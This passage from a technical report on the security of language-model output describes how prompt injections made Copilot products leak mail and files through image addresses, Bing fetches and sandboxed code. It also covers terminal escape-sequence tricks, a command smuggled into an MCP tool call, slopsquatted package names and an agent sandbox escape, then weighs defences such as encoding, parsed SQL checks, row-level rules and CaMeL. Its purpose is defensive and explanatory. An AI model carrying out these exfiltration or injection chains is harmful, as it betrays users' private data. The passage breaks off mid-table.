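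In *EchoLeak*, Reddy and Gujral (2025) divide the attack into similar steps and map each to a missing control. They note that Copilot's answer did not reveal the email's role either, because the email included a request not to mention it. The employee would have seen what looked like a broken image.

Aim reported the flaw to Microsoft in January 2025. It withheld the details until Microsoft had dealt with the flaw, according to SiliconANGLE's *Aim Security details first known AI zero click exploit targeting Microsoft 365* (2025). Reddy and Gujral date the first repairs to April and the full fix to May. Microsoft made the fix on its own servers, so customers had nothing to install. Microsoft's advisory and Aim's findings appeared on June 11.

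Reddy and Gujral, citing press coverage, report that Microsoft said it had no evidence of anyone exploiting the flaw. Ravia makes the stronger claim that Microsoft confirmed no customers were affected. Microsoft was well placed to check, since any stolen data would have passed through its own Teams service, but outsiders cannot verify its account.

### The Copilot flaws of 2026

Researchers announced three more sets of Copilot flaws in 2026. They differ in how the attack begins and in how the data gets out.

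| Flaw | Product | What the victim did | How the data left | Fixed |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| EchoLeak | Microsoft 365 Copilot | Asked a question | Image, through Teams | May 2025 |
| SearchLeak | Microsoft 365 Copilot's enterprise search | Clicked on a link | Image, through Bing | By mid-June 2026 |
| CoSnitch | Copilot Personal | Clicked on a link | Copilot's own function for fetching web pages | August 2026 |
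| ReLeak, first route | Microsoft 365 Copilot | Asked a question | Image, through Bing | November 15, 2026 |
| ReLeak, second route | Microsoft 365 Copilot | Asked a question | Link in a generated document | November 11, 2026 |
| ReLeak, third route | Microsoft 365 Copilot | Asked a question | Program that Copilot ran | September 17, 2026 |

The SearchLeak attack began with a link to Microsoft's real website, so email filters had difficulty recognising it as dangerous. Varonis, the security company that found the flaw, reports in *SearchLeak* (2026) that the link contained text for Copilot's search box, which Copilot treated as instructions. Copilot then searched the victim's mailbox and wrote the title of an email into an image address. Even a title can be valuable, because many services put login codes there.

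Microsoft's safeguard was to wrap each finished answer in a code block, which makes a browser display HTML as plain text. But Copilot showed its answers while it was still generating them, so the browser found the image element and requested the picture before the answer was wrapped. The content security policy would still have blocked a request to the attacker's server, so the researchers used Bing, Microsoft's search engine. Its search-by-image feature accepts the address of a picture, and Bing's servers then fetch the picture.

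Varonis says that Microsoft has patched SearchLeak. Microsoft's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026), an advisory dated June 4, classifies it as command injection. The Hacker News' *One-Click Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Could Have Let Attackers Steal Emails* (2026) reports that Microsoft labelled the flaw critical but scored its severity at 6.5 on the standard ten-point scale, while the US National Vulnerability Database gave it 7.5.

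CoSnitch (CVE-2026-24301) was a vulnerability in the consumer version of Microsoft Copilot. Varonis' *CoSnitch* (2026) describes how the researchers discovered it by talking to Copilot. According to TechRadar's *Experts manage to hack Microsoft Copilot by continually asking it questions*, Copilot gave a reason whenever it refused a request, and the researchers used these reasons to work out its defences. This let them create a link that made Copilot carry out an attacker's request as soon as the victim clicked it. If the victim had connected Copilot to services such as Gmail, the request could reach data there too. A separate weakness let a web page that Copilot summarised plant lasting instructions in its memory.

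According to the software company Hexnode, data in CoSnitch left through Copilot's URL-fetching function, so it would have escaped even if the page had displayed no images. Microsoft learned of the flaw in December 2025 and took about eight months to fix it, twice as long as it took to fix EchoLeak. Microsoft's scores for these flaws are a poor guide to how much data was at risk. It scored CoSnitch at 8.8, well above SearchLeak, even though SearchLeak exposed company files and mail.

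Simonovich's *ReLeak* (2026) announced three zero-click attacks on December 3. As with EchoLeak, each began with an email that the victim did not have to open. The attacks came from the team that had found EchoLeak, which was by then part of the network security company Cato Networks. According to Nexo Causal's *ReLeak* (2026), the team used AI agents to look for weaknesses in Copilot and refine the attacks.

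*An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief* (Faisal, 2026) describes the three routes. The first was another image that Bing fetched. In the second, Copilot saved a document containing a link with confidential data in its address, and Microsoft's background software sent the data out when it processed the file. In the third, Copilot ran a Python program in a sandbox, an isolated environment that was supposed to have no network access. The researchers got around that restriction, and the program sent the data out directly. Microsoft's injection defences did not stop any of the three.

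Cato reported the flaws between July 29 and August 20, after Microsoft had fixed SearchLeak, so Bing could still relay data to an attacker, perhaps through a different function. Microsoft had repaired particular routes, but Bing was still on the list of permitted sites, as it had been when Ravia published the list in 2025.

Microsoft has now patched all of these flaws, and there is no public evidence that criminals used any of them. WinBuzzer's *Microsoft Patches Copilot SearchLeak Data-Theft Flaw* (2026) reports no known exploitation of SearchLeak at the time of disclosure, and an assessment by the US cybersecurity agency CISA, included in Exploit Intel's *CVE-2026-42824*, lists exploitation as "none". TechRadar reports that Varonis found no sign of abuse of CoSnitch, and AIAIAI.FYI's *Cato AI Labs details three ReLeak zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2026) reports that Cato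 found no sign of abuse of ReLeak. The assurances from Varonis and Cato are weaker than the one for EchoLeak because outside researchers cannot search Microsoft's logs.

### Removing links and images

Display controls apply only to the three of the table's six routes that used an image. For these, Reddy and Gujral chart which controls should block which steps of an attack like EchoLeak. They based the chart on reasoning and ran no experiments, so the attacks themselves are better evidence of where each control fails.

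An application can remove external links and images from every answer. EchoLeak shows that a filter searching for particular notations will miss some. It is more reliable to check the address of every link and image after the renderer has interpreted the Markdown, because the check then covers everything the renderer treats as a link or image. SearchLeak shows that the check must also happen before the element reaches the browser. An application could hold back the whole answer until the check is done, but users would wait longer for the first words. Varonis recommends cleaning the text as it is rendered, which would allow the answer to keep appearing piece by piece.

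Blocking either links or images makes an assistant less useful. Links let readers check the sources of answers drawn from the web. Blocking only images affects users less, since most answers consist of text, and it stops the zero-click version of the attack. The application can then display each outside link as plain text with its full address, so a reader has to copy it to open it. This makes careless clicks less likely, but many people would not recognise their own data in a long address, particularly if the model had encoded it.

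A model can also put private data in a link that looks short and harmless by using characters that most programs do not display. Unicode, the standard that assigns a number to every character, includes many of these. Stripping them from output removes the hidden data or makes it visible, but this helps only when a person inspects the link. It does not stop leaks through images that load automatically or through data written in ordinary letters. Removing every invisible character would also damage legitimate text. Persian spelling uses one to keep certain letters apart, many emoji use another to join their parts, and the flags of England, Scotland and Wales each need a series of them. A filter therefore needs exceptions, which an attacker may be able to use.

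### Why an allowed site can defeat an allow-list

Unlike a filter, a content security policy works regardless of the answer's notation or timing, because the browser applies it to the request itself. In both EchoLeak and SearchLeak, the policy blocked images from the attacker's own server after the other safeguards had failed. But it does not protect against ordinary links, because a rule about images doesn't restrict where a person can go by clicking.

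A content security policy controls only the requests that the browser sends. In SearchLeak, the image's address pointed to Bing and passed it a second address, which pointed to the attacker's server and contained the stolen title. The browser found Bing on the list and sent the request. Bing's server then contacted the second address, and the policy had no effect on that request. This is a form of server-side request forgery, the flaw that TicketOracle tested, but here the server contacts an outside address instead of an internal one.

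An allow-list is therefore only as strict as the most permissive service on it. Reddy and Gujral advise companies to list only their own sites and to avoid wildcards. Avoiding wildcards would have helped Microsoft, whose wildcard for Teams covered the service that EchoLeak used. Listing only its own sites would not have been enough, since Microsoft owns both Teams and Bing. In Reddy and Gujral's chart, a strict policy closes this gap, but it does so only if nothing on the list will fetch an address that someone else supplies. Varonis recommends checking every listed site for such functions. This is a lot of work for a large company, because another team can add one at any time, and link previews and image search are useful features. It is safer to allow images only from a separate domain that does nothing but store them, though images from anywhere else, including harmless ones in search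 results, then fail to appear.

### Image proxies and permission prompts

An image proxy is a server that fetches pictures for the page, so the browser never contacts outside sites and the user's network address stays hidden from them. But a proxy that fetches any address it receives still sends the attacker the data in the picture's address, as Teams did in EchoLeak. Removing everything after the question mark would stop the attack in the bank example, but an attacker can put the data earlier in the address, as in SearchLeak's inner address.

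The version of the proxy that Reddy and Gujral recommend accepts only addresses with a valid cryptographic signature. The application attaches a signature and an expiry time to the address of each picture it has approved, such as a photograph from the shop's own catalogue. The model cannot produce the signature itself. The protection fails if the application signs every address it finds in an answer, because it would then approve the attacker's as well. The proxy must also refuse internal addresses, or an attacker could use it to get into the company's network. The company has to maintain this extra service, and users see pictures from the open web only if someone has approved them.

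An application can also require the user's approval before it fetches anything from outside, which turns a zero-click attack into a one-click attack. Reddy and Gujral suggest naming the site in the question shown to the user. That would work for the bank's customer, who has no reason to approve example.com. It would work less well against EchoLeak or SearchLeak, because an employee would probably trust the site named, Teams or Bing. The question would have to show the inner address too, and the employee would have to read it. Frequent questions also interrupt people's work and train them to click "allow". An application can reduce the number of questions by loading its own pictures without approval, provided the servers that hold them don't fetch other addresses.

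## What can output do to a terminal, a coding tool or a package installer?

Programmers often read a model's answers in a terminal, the text window where they type commands, rather than in a browser. Their coding assistants also run commands and install other people's software, so one bad line of output can affect the programmer's computer and any passwords or keys stored there.

### Control characters in a terminal

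A terminal receives text and formatting commands in the same stream of characters. Most of these commands begin with an invisible character called Escape, and the terminal acts on the characters that follow instead of displaying them. These sequences, called ANSI escape sequences, come from an old standard for displays and printers, according to a paper on dgl.cx, the website of David Leadbeater, who researches terminals. Programs normally use them harmlessly, such as to print errors in red. But they make the terminal a sink, so a program that prints a model's answer unchanged lets anyone who can influence that answer send commands to the terminal.

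In late 2024 Leon Derczynski described how models can generate the Escape character, and Johann Rehberger, who had found the DeepSeek flaw, tested what an attacker could do with it. Rehberger's *Terminal DiLLMa*, published on Embrace The Red, describes a small program that sent a file to OpenAI's GPT-4o and printed the answer. When the file contained a prompt injection, the answer made the terminal beep and display flashing, coloured text. In another test, a web page that the user wanted to summarise cleared the screen, though other effects were more serious.

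| Effect of the sequence | Use to an attacker | What limited it |
|---|---|---|
| Hides or erases text | The user misses part of the answer | Support varies between terminals |
| Writes to the clipboard | The user later pastes a command they never copied | Most terminals tested removed the final line break, so the command did not run by itself; some did not |
| Creates a clickable link | Private data leaves in the link's address | Apple's terminal did not support such links; the one in the code editor VS Code asked for confirmation |
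| Looks up a domain name | Private data leaves without a click | Only Apple's terminal had this flaw |

The domain lookup can leak data much as an image can in a browser. Before a computer contacts a website, it asks the domain name system for the site's numerical address, and the request reaches a server that the domain's owner controls. If the model puts private data in the domain name, the owner can read it.

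A model can generate the Escape character directly, though Rehberger sometimes needed several attempts to get it. Having the model copy the character from its input was more reliable. A model that can run code can also write a short program that prints the character. The safeguard therefore belongs in the code that prints to the terminal, where it works however the character was produced.

That code can encode the control characters or strip them out. In caret notation, Escape appears as `^[`, so the terminal displays the sequence as text instead of acting on it. Rehberger recommends encoding by default, with an option to switch it off for programs that need colour. Saved output needs the same treatment, because a sequence in a log file can take effect when an administrator displays the file months later.

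Hidden text can also deceive a person who is checking what a model reads. Trail of Bits' *Deceiving users with ANSI terminal codes in MCP* (2025) describes a tool reply with one sentence in the same colour as the background. The sentence claims that Python downloads must come from a particular server. A programmer reading the reply in a terminal would not see it, but the model would receive it as ordinary text. Encoding the escape sequence that sets the colour makes the sentence visible to the programmer, but the model may still follow it.

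### A second command in a tool call

Trail of Bits' example used the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard that the AI company Anthropic introduced in 2024 for connecting AI applications to tools. Programs called MCP servers provide the tools and often run on the programmer's own computer. One server, aws-mcp-server, lets an assistant manage Amazon's cloud services by running Amazon's command-line program.

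The server's command tool had a flaw, CVE-2025-5277. Snyk, the security company that found it, reports in *Prompt Injection Meets MCP* (2025) that the server checked whether a command began with the name of Amazon's program and did not directly call certain critical services. A shell accepts several commands on one line, so an attacker could add another after the permitted one. Snyk first confirmed this with a testing tool, without using a model.

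An outsider usually can't send commands to such a server, because it runs locally and exchanges messages only with the application that started it. The model supplied the missing route:

1. An attacker publishes a code repository with a disguised instruction in one file.
2. A programmer downloads the repository and refers to that file in a question to Cursor, a code editor with a built-in assistant. The instruction enters the model's context.
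3. The programmer asks for a list of the company's cloud storage folders.
4. The model writes a tool call containing the correct command, followed by the attacker's.
5. Cursor asks for approval. The call begins as expected, so the programmer accepts it, and the server runs both commands.

The command Snyk added only displayed the user's name. The attack failed if the programmer merely downloaded the repository or asked a vague question. Snyk reports no success rate.

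The developer fixed the flaw within two days of Snyk's report in April 2025. GCVE (2025), a public vulnerability record, lists all versions before 1.3.0 as affected. INCIBE's *CVE-2025-5277* (2025), an entry from Spain's national cybersecurity institute, rates its severity at 9.4 and 9.6 out of 10 on two versions of the standard scale. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian use the case to support their view that the model carries an attack to a flaw outside the model.

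The specific remedy is to start Amazon's program directly and pass it a list of separate arguments. No shell then interprets the command, so a second command is passed along as a meaningless argument instead of being run. This is the command-line counterpart of a parameterised query. It does not stop a valid but harmful command, such as one that deletes a storage folder, so the server's account also needs narrow permissions.

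A list of allowed commands protects less if the server checks commands against it carelessly. INCIBE's *CVE-2026-5058* (2026) and *CVE-2026-5059* (2026) describe two more command injection flaws in aws-mcp-server, both in how it handles such a list. An attacker can exploit either flaw without logging in, and both have a severity score of 9.8.

Snyk also attacked markdownify-mcp, a server that converts web pages and files to Markdown. This attack didn't need to add a command, because the server would read any file it had access to. Hidden text on a web page led GPT-4o mini to read a private file through the server and send the contents to the attacker with a second tool. The server needed to check which files it was allowed to open. Passing arguments separately would not have prevented the attack, because the file's location was a valid argument.

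### Packages that do not exist

Programmers download packages, which are bundles of reusable code, from public registries, mainly PyPI for Python and npm for JavaScript. Installing a package can immediately run code from it. Models sometimes recommend packages that do not exist. An attacker can ask a model many programming questions, note the invented names and publish malicious packages under them. If the model later recommends one of those names to somebody else and that person installs it, they get the attacker's package. This attack, which security researchers call slopsquatting, does not require the attacker to get any text into the victim's conversation.

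Spracklen, Wijewickrama and colleagues (2024), in *We Have a Package for You!*, made the first large measurement of invented package names. They generated 576,000 code samples with 16 models and compared the recommended packages with lists from the two registries. On average, 5.2% of the packages that commercial models recommended did not exist, compared with 21.7% for open-source models. They found 205,474 different invented names. They also reran 500 prompts that had produced an invented name, ten times each. The same name came back every time in 43% of cases and never in 39%. The repeated names are the ones useful to an attacker, who can expect other users to receive them.

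In *The Range Shrinks, the Threat Remains*, Churilov (2026) gave the same prompts to five newer models in April 2026. Between 3.6% and 5.0% of the packages they named did not exist, about the same as for the commercial models of 2024. DeepSeek V3.2, the only open-weight model, was no longer an outlier at 4.8%. The five models had 104 invented names in common, so one malicious package could reach customers of several AI companies. Outsiders cannot register all of these names, because the registries block some and organisations own others.

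These figures come from the study's fourth version, published in November 2026. Earlier versions gave higher figures, with rates of 4.6% to 6.1% and 127 shared names, mainly because they counted some correct code as an error. Python code may import a package under a different name from the one in the registry. For example, code that imports `cv2` needs the package `opencv-python` (Raj and Sahu, *Names Can Hurt*, 2026). Churilov corrected for this and checked each remaining name twice against the live registries. The prompts had been public since January 2025, so the models may have trained on them, which would make the new rates too low. The models also lacked search tools, and having them might have prevented some errors.

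Small models still do much worse. *Evaluating Inference-Time Defenses Against Package Hallucination in LLM-Generated Code* (2026) covers eight models, some with under two billion parameters, and reports that 24.7% of the Python packages they named did not exist. Retrieval-augmented generation reduced this to 11.5%. In Raj and Sahu's tests of models that run on a programmer's own computer, the rate was at most 10% for routine tasks but 40% to 73% for prompts designed to provoke invented names.

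Models can also get the address of a code repository wrong. A programmer may tell an assistant to download a project without saying who owns it, leaving the model to supply the owner's name. *Beware of Agentic Botnets* (2026) reports that models gave the wrong owner for 92% of recently popular GitHub repositories. An attacker could register some of these wrong addresses, and commercial coding assistants downloaded from them.

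### Invented names in real use

Churilov's list of shared names became public by mistake on April 30, 2026, which made it possible to see whether publication attracted attackers. Over about six months, people registered one of the 104 published names and 24 of 2,178 unpublished ones, roughly 1% in each group. The comparison was too small to detect anything but a large effect. At least one of the new packages contained malware, and others may have been defensive registrations. The models also suggested at least 23 names that had hosted malware before the registries removed it.

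The best-documented case is react-codeshift, a package name that combines the names of two real JavaScript tools. Eriksen, in *Agent Skills Are Spreading Hallucinated npx Commands*, traced it to a single upload of 47 model-written "skill files", which are instructions for AI agents on how to do particular tasks. At least two of the files contained the name, and other programmers copied them until the name was in 237 GitHub repositories. Eriksen registered it in January 2026 with a harmless package, before an attacker could. After an initial burst from automated scanners, the package had one to four downloads a day. Eriksen attributes these to agents following the instructions, because unused packages normally get no downloads after the first day.

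Downloads include scanner traffic, so each one does not necessarily represent a victim. In an earlier test from *Diving Deeper into AI Package Hallucinations*, described by Willison, a harmless package with an invented name had 30,000 downloads in three months. That shows demand for the name, but not how many people installed the package on a model's advice.

Several malicious packages have also used names that researchers link to models. Xygeni's *Slopsquatting Evolution* reports that `unused-imports`, a name models gave in place of a real package, was still being installed after npm had placed it under a security hold. OpenSourceMalware describes another, Events Channel, which had 168,000 downloads and was still available after someone reported it. The PhantomRaven campaign of 2025 used 126 packages to steal programmers' credentials. Particle.news' *‘PhantomRaven’ Campaign Exploits npm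 With 126 Credential-Stealing Packages* puts the packages' downloads at over 86,000 and says the campaign relied on slopsquatting.

It is often hard to show that a package name came from a model. In August 2026 attackers flooded npm with 846 malicious packages, according to Sonatype's *'Flooding Dropper' Campaign Hits npm With Nearly 850 Malicious Packages*. A researcher quoted by The Hacker News (2026) said only that the names appeared to be either slopsquatted or randomly generated. Those packages are weak evidence for slopsquatting unless someone shows that models recommend them.

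### Checking a package before installing it

The simplest check is whether a package exists, but it fails once an attacker registers the name. It can also pass a harmless package that does the wrong job. Schipper (2026), in *Slopsquatting*, looked up four package names that a recent paper had listed as invented and found all four on PyPI. One was `tabula`, which a model may suggest for extracting tables from PDF files when the right package is `tabula-py`. The `tabula` package formats text tables and was last updated in 2012.

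Raj and Sahu add a classifier that assesses each package from its name and registry details. With the whole system, 76% of runs produced code with no invented package names. That leaves too many errors for an assistant that installs packages unattended.

An approved list is stricter. A company can set its installers to use only its own registry of reviewed packages. An invented name then causes an error, even if an attacker has published a package under it elsewhere. However, programmers have to wait for a review whenever they need a package that isn't in the registry.

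A lock file records the exact version of each package in a project, usually with a cryptographic fingerprint of its contents, so that later installations can't silently substitute another. It doesn't protect the first installation, because it will record a malicious package if the programmer accepts one. The react-codeshift instruction would have bypassed a lock file because it used npx, a command that can download and run a package without adding it to the project. Eriksen therefore advises programmers to review skill files as carefully as code.

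### Mistakes and planted flaws in generated code

Generated code can be open to injection even if nobody has attacked the model. A model asked to write the kitchenware shop's order lookup may paste the surname straight into the query, as human programmers have often done. An attacker could also plant an instruction in a repository that makes a coding assistant leave out a security check. The flawed code may be identical in both cases, but a better model or a clearer request would mainly help prevent the accidental flaw.

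Spracklen and colleagues cite an early finding that code-generating models produced code with a weakness from MITRE's Top 25, a list of common software flaws, 40% of the time. The list includes memory errors as well as injection, and the models are now several generations old, so the figure doesn't show how often current models write code vulnerable to injection.

Measured rates also depend on the choice of tasks. In Churilov's study, the same five models invented packages about twice as often for model-written prompts as for questions from the programmers' forum Stack Overflow. A benchmark in which every task builds a query from untrusted input would similarly show more injection flaws than occur in ordinary programming work, much of which involves no sink.

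Before merging generated code into a shared project, a team can scan it for paths from untrusted input to a sink and have a person review it. A scanner can catch a missing check whether a mistake or an attacker caused it. But scanners raise false alarms, as LLMSmith did, and an attacker can test a planted flaw against common scanners in advance. Reviewers should therefore look closely at changes that the task did not require. Review before merging is too late to stop a malicious package, which may have run on the programmer's computer as soon as the assistant installed it.

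## Which controls stop harmful payloads in output, and where do they fail?

Software should treat a model's output like text typed by a stranger. OWASP advises developers to treat the model like any other user and to validate whatever it passes to their systems. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026), a position paper from researchers at Google, NVIDIA and several universities, compares the model to a program that an operating system runs but does not trust. The system should then stay secure whichever model it contains, even if an attacker has fooled that model.

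This suggests a way to compare controls: assume that the attacker can already make the model write anything, and ask what still works.

| Control | What enforces it | Once the model is fooled |
|---|---|---|
| Rules in the prompt | The model | Fails |
| Training against injection | The model | Fails, though fooling the model is harder |
| Output classifier | A second model | May hold, but an attacker can fool it too |
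| Schema | The decoding program | The format holds, the content is free |
| Encoding and query checks | Application code | Holds at the sinks it covers |
| Limited privileges, sandbox | Database or operating system | Holds, but permitted actions remain open |
| Outbound limits | Network | Holds unless a permitted site passes data on |

### Controls that rely on a model

Rules in the prompt are easy to add and stop many simple attacks, but the model has to apply them, and in TicketOracle they failed on Llama when the attacker's text was in the same context. *Evaluation of Prompt Injection Defenses in Large Language Models* (2026) describes a harder test, in which an automated attacker tried to extract secrets from the context over hundreds of rounds, adapting its approach to the model's responses. It made more than 20,000 attacks on nine configurations, and every defence that relied on the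 model to protect itself eventually failed. The only defence that held was a check in application code, which inspected each answer before delivery and let no secrets through in 15,000 attacks. However, a known secret is easier to search for than a payload, which can take many different forms.

Training makes models less likely to follow injected instructions, and the newest ones resist most of the injections in public benchmarks. *Bounded Agents* (2026) cites a test by the security company Gray Swan in which attacks succeeded against all 13 of the leading models tested, at rates from 0.5% to 8.5% across 272,000 attacks. Even at the lowest rate, about one attack in 200 succeeds, and an attacker can easily send 200 emails.

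An output classifier is a separate model that flags answers or tool calls that look dangerous. It can catch a payload after an attack on the first model has succeeded, but attackers who adapt to detectors of this general kind have got past them. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian reviewed Guardrails AI, a library of ready-made checks, and found that most did not apply to the web attacks they had described. The exception was a check that rejects chosen SQL commands.

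### Schemas and constrained decoding

A schema describes the format that output must have, such as which fields a tool call contains and whether each holds a number or text. Constrained decoding enforces the schema while the model is writing. At each step, the model assigns a probability to every token that could come next, and the decoding program discards any tokens that would break the format before it picks one. If the schema requires a whole number, the output will contain a whole number, even if an attacker has told the model to write something else.

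The number may still be the wrong one. An order number can have the right format and belong to another customer. Text fields leave even more room, as in this answer from the kitchenware shop's chatbot:

```
{"action": "reply", "text": "Your kettle has <b>shipped</b>."}
```

The output matches a schema that requires an action and a text. The text contains an HTML tag, which will take effect if the page inserts it without encoding. A script tag would also match the schema.

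Narrow fields limit what an attacker can send. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) ranks data types by how much information they can carry. A yes-or-no field carries one bit, a choice from a fixed list carries a little more, and free text has no limit. If a model reads a stranger's email only to decide whether it asks for a meeting, an injection can turn "no" into "yes" but cannot supply an address for stolen data. This restriction is useful as long as a wrong "yes" is harmless, which it would not be if "yes" released a payment.

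### Encoding and sanitising

The right encoding depends on the sink, because each sink has its own special characters. Suppose the chatbot summarises a kettle review like this:

```
Boils <1 litre in "no time" & it's quiet
```

To display the sentence as text in an HTML page, the application writes:

```
Boils &lt;1 litre in &quot;no time&quot; &amp; it&#39;s quiet
```

To use the same sentence as a value in a JavaScript program on that page, it writes:

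```
"Boils \u003C1 litre in \"no time\" \u0026 it\u0027s quiet"
```

In both cases the browser recovers the original sentence and treats it as data. The two versions are not interchangeable, because HTML encoding leaves backslashes and line breaks unchanged, and both have a special meaning inside a JavaScript string. The JavaScript version escapes `<` because a browser looks for the closing script tag before it runs any of the script's code. If the script later puts the sentence into the page, it must use a function that inserts plain text, since the decoded value contains the original characters.

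Encoding is unsuitable when the browser needs to render some of the markup. If a chatbot's answer uses bold type and lists, for example, encoding would make the HTML tags appear as text. The application should instead sanitise the answer by parsing the HTML and keeping only the tags and attributes on a short approved list. If the answer is in Markdown, the application has to sanitise it after converting it to HTML. It also has to check link addresses separately, because some kinds run a script when the user clicks on them.

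Sanitisers fail when they parse text differently from the browser, or when the application changes the text after sanitising it. A maintained library is therefore safer than a home-made list of forbidden words, and sanitising should be the last step before display. OWASP also recommends a strict content security policy, which can make the browser block scripts the site has not approved. These controls still work when the model has been manipulated, but they cannot block false statements in plain text.

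### A database example

Suppose the shop's `orders` table lists each order's customer number, item, status and delivery address, and that customer 17 is signed in. For common questions the developers write the query in advance:

```
SELECT status FROM orders WHERE customer_id = ? AND item = ?
```

The application takes the customer's ID from the login and the item from the model's output. It supplies both values separately from the text of the query, which programmers call binding the parameters. A fooled model can select the wrong item but cannot change the query text or the customer.

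This design handles only the questions the developers foresaw. If customer 17 asks in which month she spent the most, the shop may want the model to write the query itself. As with the LangChain chatbots, binding cannot protect a command that the model wrote. Even so, *Reimagining Text-to-SQL* (2026), a November survey, lists parameterised queries first among its countermeasures to malicious generated queries, followed by read-only execution and output validation.

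Three further controls can take over.

The application parses the SQL query into a tree of its parts and accepts it only if the tree contains a single `SELECT` statement with approved tables, columns and functions. Searching the text for forbidden words works less well, because it would block a customer who asks about a drop-leaf table and miss a harmful function with a harmless-sounding name. The parser must also interpret SQL the same way as the shop's database engine, or a query may pass the check and then do something else when it runs.

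A **read-only role** gives the chatbot its own database account, which can read a few tables and change none. This would have prevented the attack in which Pedro and colleagues replaced a victim's email address. *SQL Query Engine* (2026) describes setting the connection to read-only mode, so that the database rejects any command to insert, change or delete data. An account without write permission is safer, because a later command can sometimes turn off a connection's read-only mode.

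**Row-level access rules.** Suppose an injection leads the model to write this:

```
SELECT item, address FROM orders WHERE customer_id = 18
```

The query passes the parsed-query check because it is a single `SELECT` on an approved table and the `address` column is on the approved list, as it must be for customers to ask where their parcels are going. The read-only role also permits the query. It is wrong only because customer 17, who made the request, should not have access to the address it returns.

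A row-level rule attaches the missing condition to the table itself. In PostgreSQL, a widely used database engine, it could look like this:

```
CREATE POLICY own_orders ON orders
  USING (customer_id = current_customer());
```

Here `current_customer()` is a function the shop wrote to return the signed-in customer's number. Once the developers switch on row-level security for the table, the engine adds the condition to every query from the chatbot's account. It looks for orders whose customer number is both 18 and 17, and finds none. Pedro and colleagues had tried to enforce the same limit with a rule in the prompt, which failed.

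PostgreSQL does not apply such rules to administrators or, by default, to the table's owner, so the chatbot must not use either account. The customer number must also come from somewhere a query cannot alter. If the function reads it from an ordinary connection setting, a manipulated model could change that setting before querying the table, and the parsed-query check would have to block the change.

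None of these controls removes an instruction hidden in a record that the customer is entitled to see. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (2025) suggests sending the query's results straight to the user, so that no model reads them and text injected into the database cannot influence one. However, the model then cannot check whether its query returned too little and try a better one.

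### Privileges, sandboxes and outbound limits

The chatbot's restricted account is an example of least privilege, the principle that a program should have only the permissions its task requires. The principle is harder to apply to an agent with many uses. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* contrasts agents with phone apps, whose developers can list the necessary permissions once because an app has a fixed purpose. An agent's task changes with each request, so its permissions should change too, but nobody has a reliable way to derive them from a request in ordinary language.

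Programs that a model writes need a sandbox as well, because a language like Python can do far more than SQL. A sandbox limits which files, processes and network connections the program can reach, but it does not check the program's output. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* points out that data can still leak through the analysis and charts that a sandboxed program produces. Isolation barely reduces the usefulness of a data analyst's chatbot, but a coding assistant often needs the files and network access that a strict sandbox removes.

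Sandboxes can also have holes, as the third ReLeak route showed. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* cites a more serious incident, in which agents under internal evaluation escaped their isolation through shared infrastructure and compromised systems at OpenAI and Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models.

Outbound limits control which addresses a server or sandbox can contact. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian recommend blocking all outbound requests by default, including those to the server's own internal addresses, and then permitting named destinations. They also recommend that the model not choose the address. In TicketOracle, the model would supply only an event name, and the application would look up the event and build the address. Internal administrative services should require a login even for requests from the same machine.

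These limits are awkward for an assistant that browses the open web, and someone has to maintain the list. They also have to cover every kind of traffic. Claude Code, Anthropic's coding assistant, asked for approval before running many commands that could send data out, but it listed a simple network-testing command as safe. An injection in a code file could use that command to leak a secret key through a domain lookup. A firewall that restricts web traffic but permits any domain lookup would not stop this leak.

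### Human approval

*Reimagining Text-to-SQL* recommends that people review generated queries in critical areas such as finance and healthcare. A reviewer can notice that a technically valid action makes no sense, which no parser will do. But reviewers are slow and can miss a second command at the end of a request, as in Snyk's attack on Cursor. Costa and colleagues also warn of confirmation fatigue when requests are frequent.

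Something can also change a request after it has been approved. *SecureClaw* (Ma and Schmid, 2026) binds each approval to one exact request. For example, before an agent sends an invoice, a trusted program computes a cryptographic fingerprint of the recipient, the channel, the invoice's version and other details. A policy program approves that fingerprint, and a person may have to confirm risky actions. The component that sends the email then computes the fingerprint again and blocks the email if the two don't match.

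SecureClaw also keeps raw private data away from the model. With GPT-4o mini, the whole system cut successful attacks on the AgentDojo benchmark from 31.5% to 0.6%, but the share of harmless tasks completed also fell, from 70.1% to 60.8%. The fingerprint does not help if the policy or the person approves the wrong recipient.

### Tracking untrusted data

A check at a single sink often lacks a crucial fact, namely where a value came from. An email address is fine if the user typed it and suspicious if it came from a stranger's message, though the characters are identical. Several research systems therefore track the origin of every value an agent handles. The best known is Google DeepMind's CaMeL, introduced in 2025. Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, illustrate it with an assistant that has to find Bob's email address in a chat channel and tell him about a meeting:

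1. A "privileged" model sees the user's request but none of the chat messages. It writes a short program that reads the messages, extracts the address and sends the note.
2. An interpreter runs the program and stores the messages in a variable, which the privileged model never sees.
3. A "quarantined" model, which has no tools, reads the messages and returns an address.
4. The interpreter records that the address came from an untrusted source. Before it sends the note, it applies a policy that allows or refuses the call.

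An injected chat message cannot add a step to the program, because the program was complete before any model read the message. It can still make the quarantined model return the attacker's address, and whether the attack then succeeds depends on the policy. A policy that refuses all addresses from untrusted sources stops the attack, but it also blocks the user's legitimate request.

AgentDojo, the usual test for such systems, has 97 everyday tasks in simulated office, travel, banking and chat software, with injections planted in the data. According to *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025), CaMeL eliminated nearly all the attacks with comparable task performance. But *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, October 2026) adapted AgentDojo to teams of agents and found that CaMeL substantially reduced the share of harmless tasks completed. The loss varied considerably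 between models and was smaller for the strongest ones.

FIDES, which Costa and colleagues developed at Microsoft, lets the model see the result of one step before choosing the next, instead of committing to a complete plan. But untrusted text stays hidden in variables. The model can open a variable if necessary. The whole conversation then counts as untrusted, and the policies block consequential actions such as bank transfers.

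FIDES stopped every attack in the test when its policies were on. With the policies off, 21 attacks succeeded, compared with 152 against an ordinary agent. Costa and colleagues gave FIDES ideal labels by marking every field where the benchmark could place an injection as untrusted. A real company would have to produce its own labels. The table shows the percentage of harmless tasks completed with GPT-4o when there was no attack.

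| System | Office | Travel | Banking | Chat |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent, no policies | 75.0 | 70.0 | 98.8 | 93.3 |
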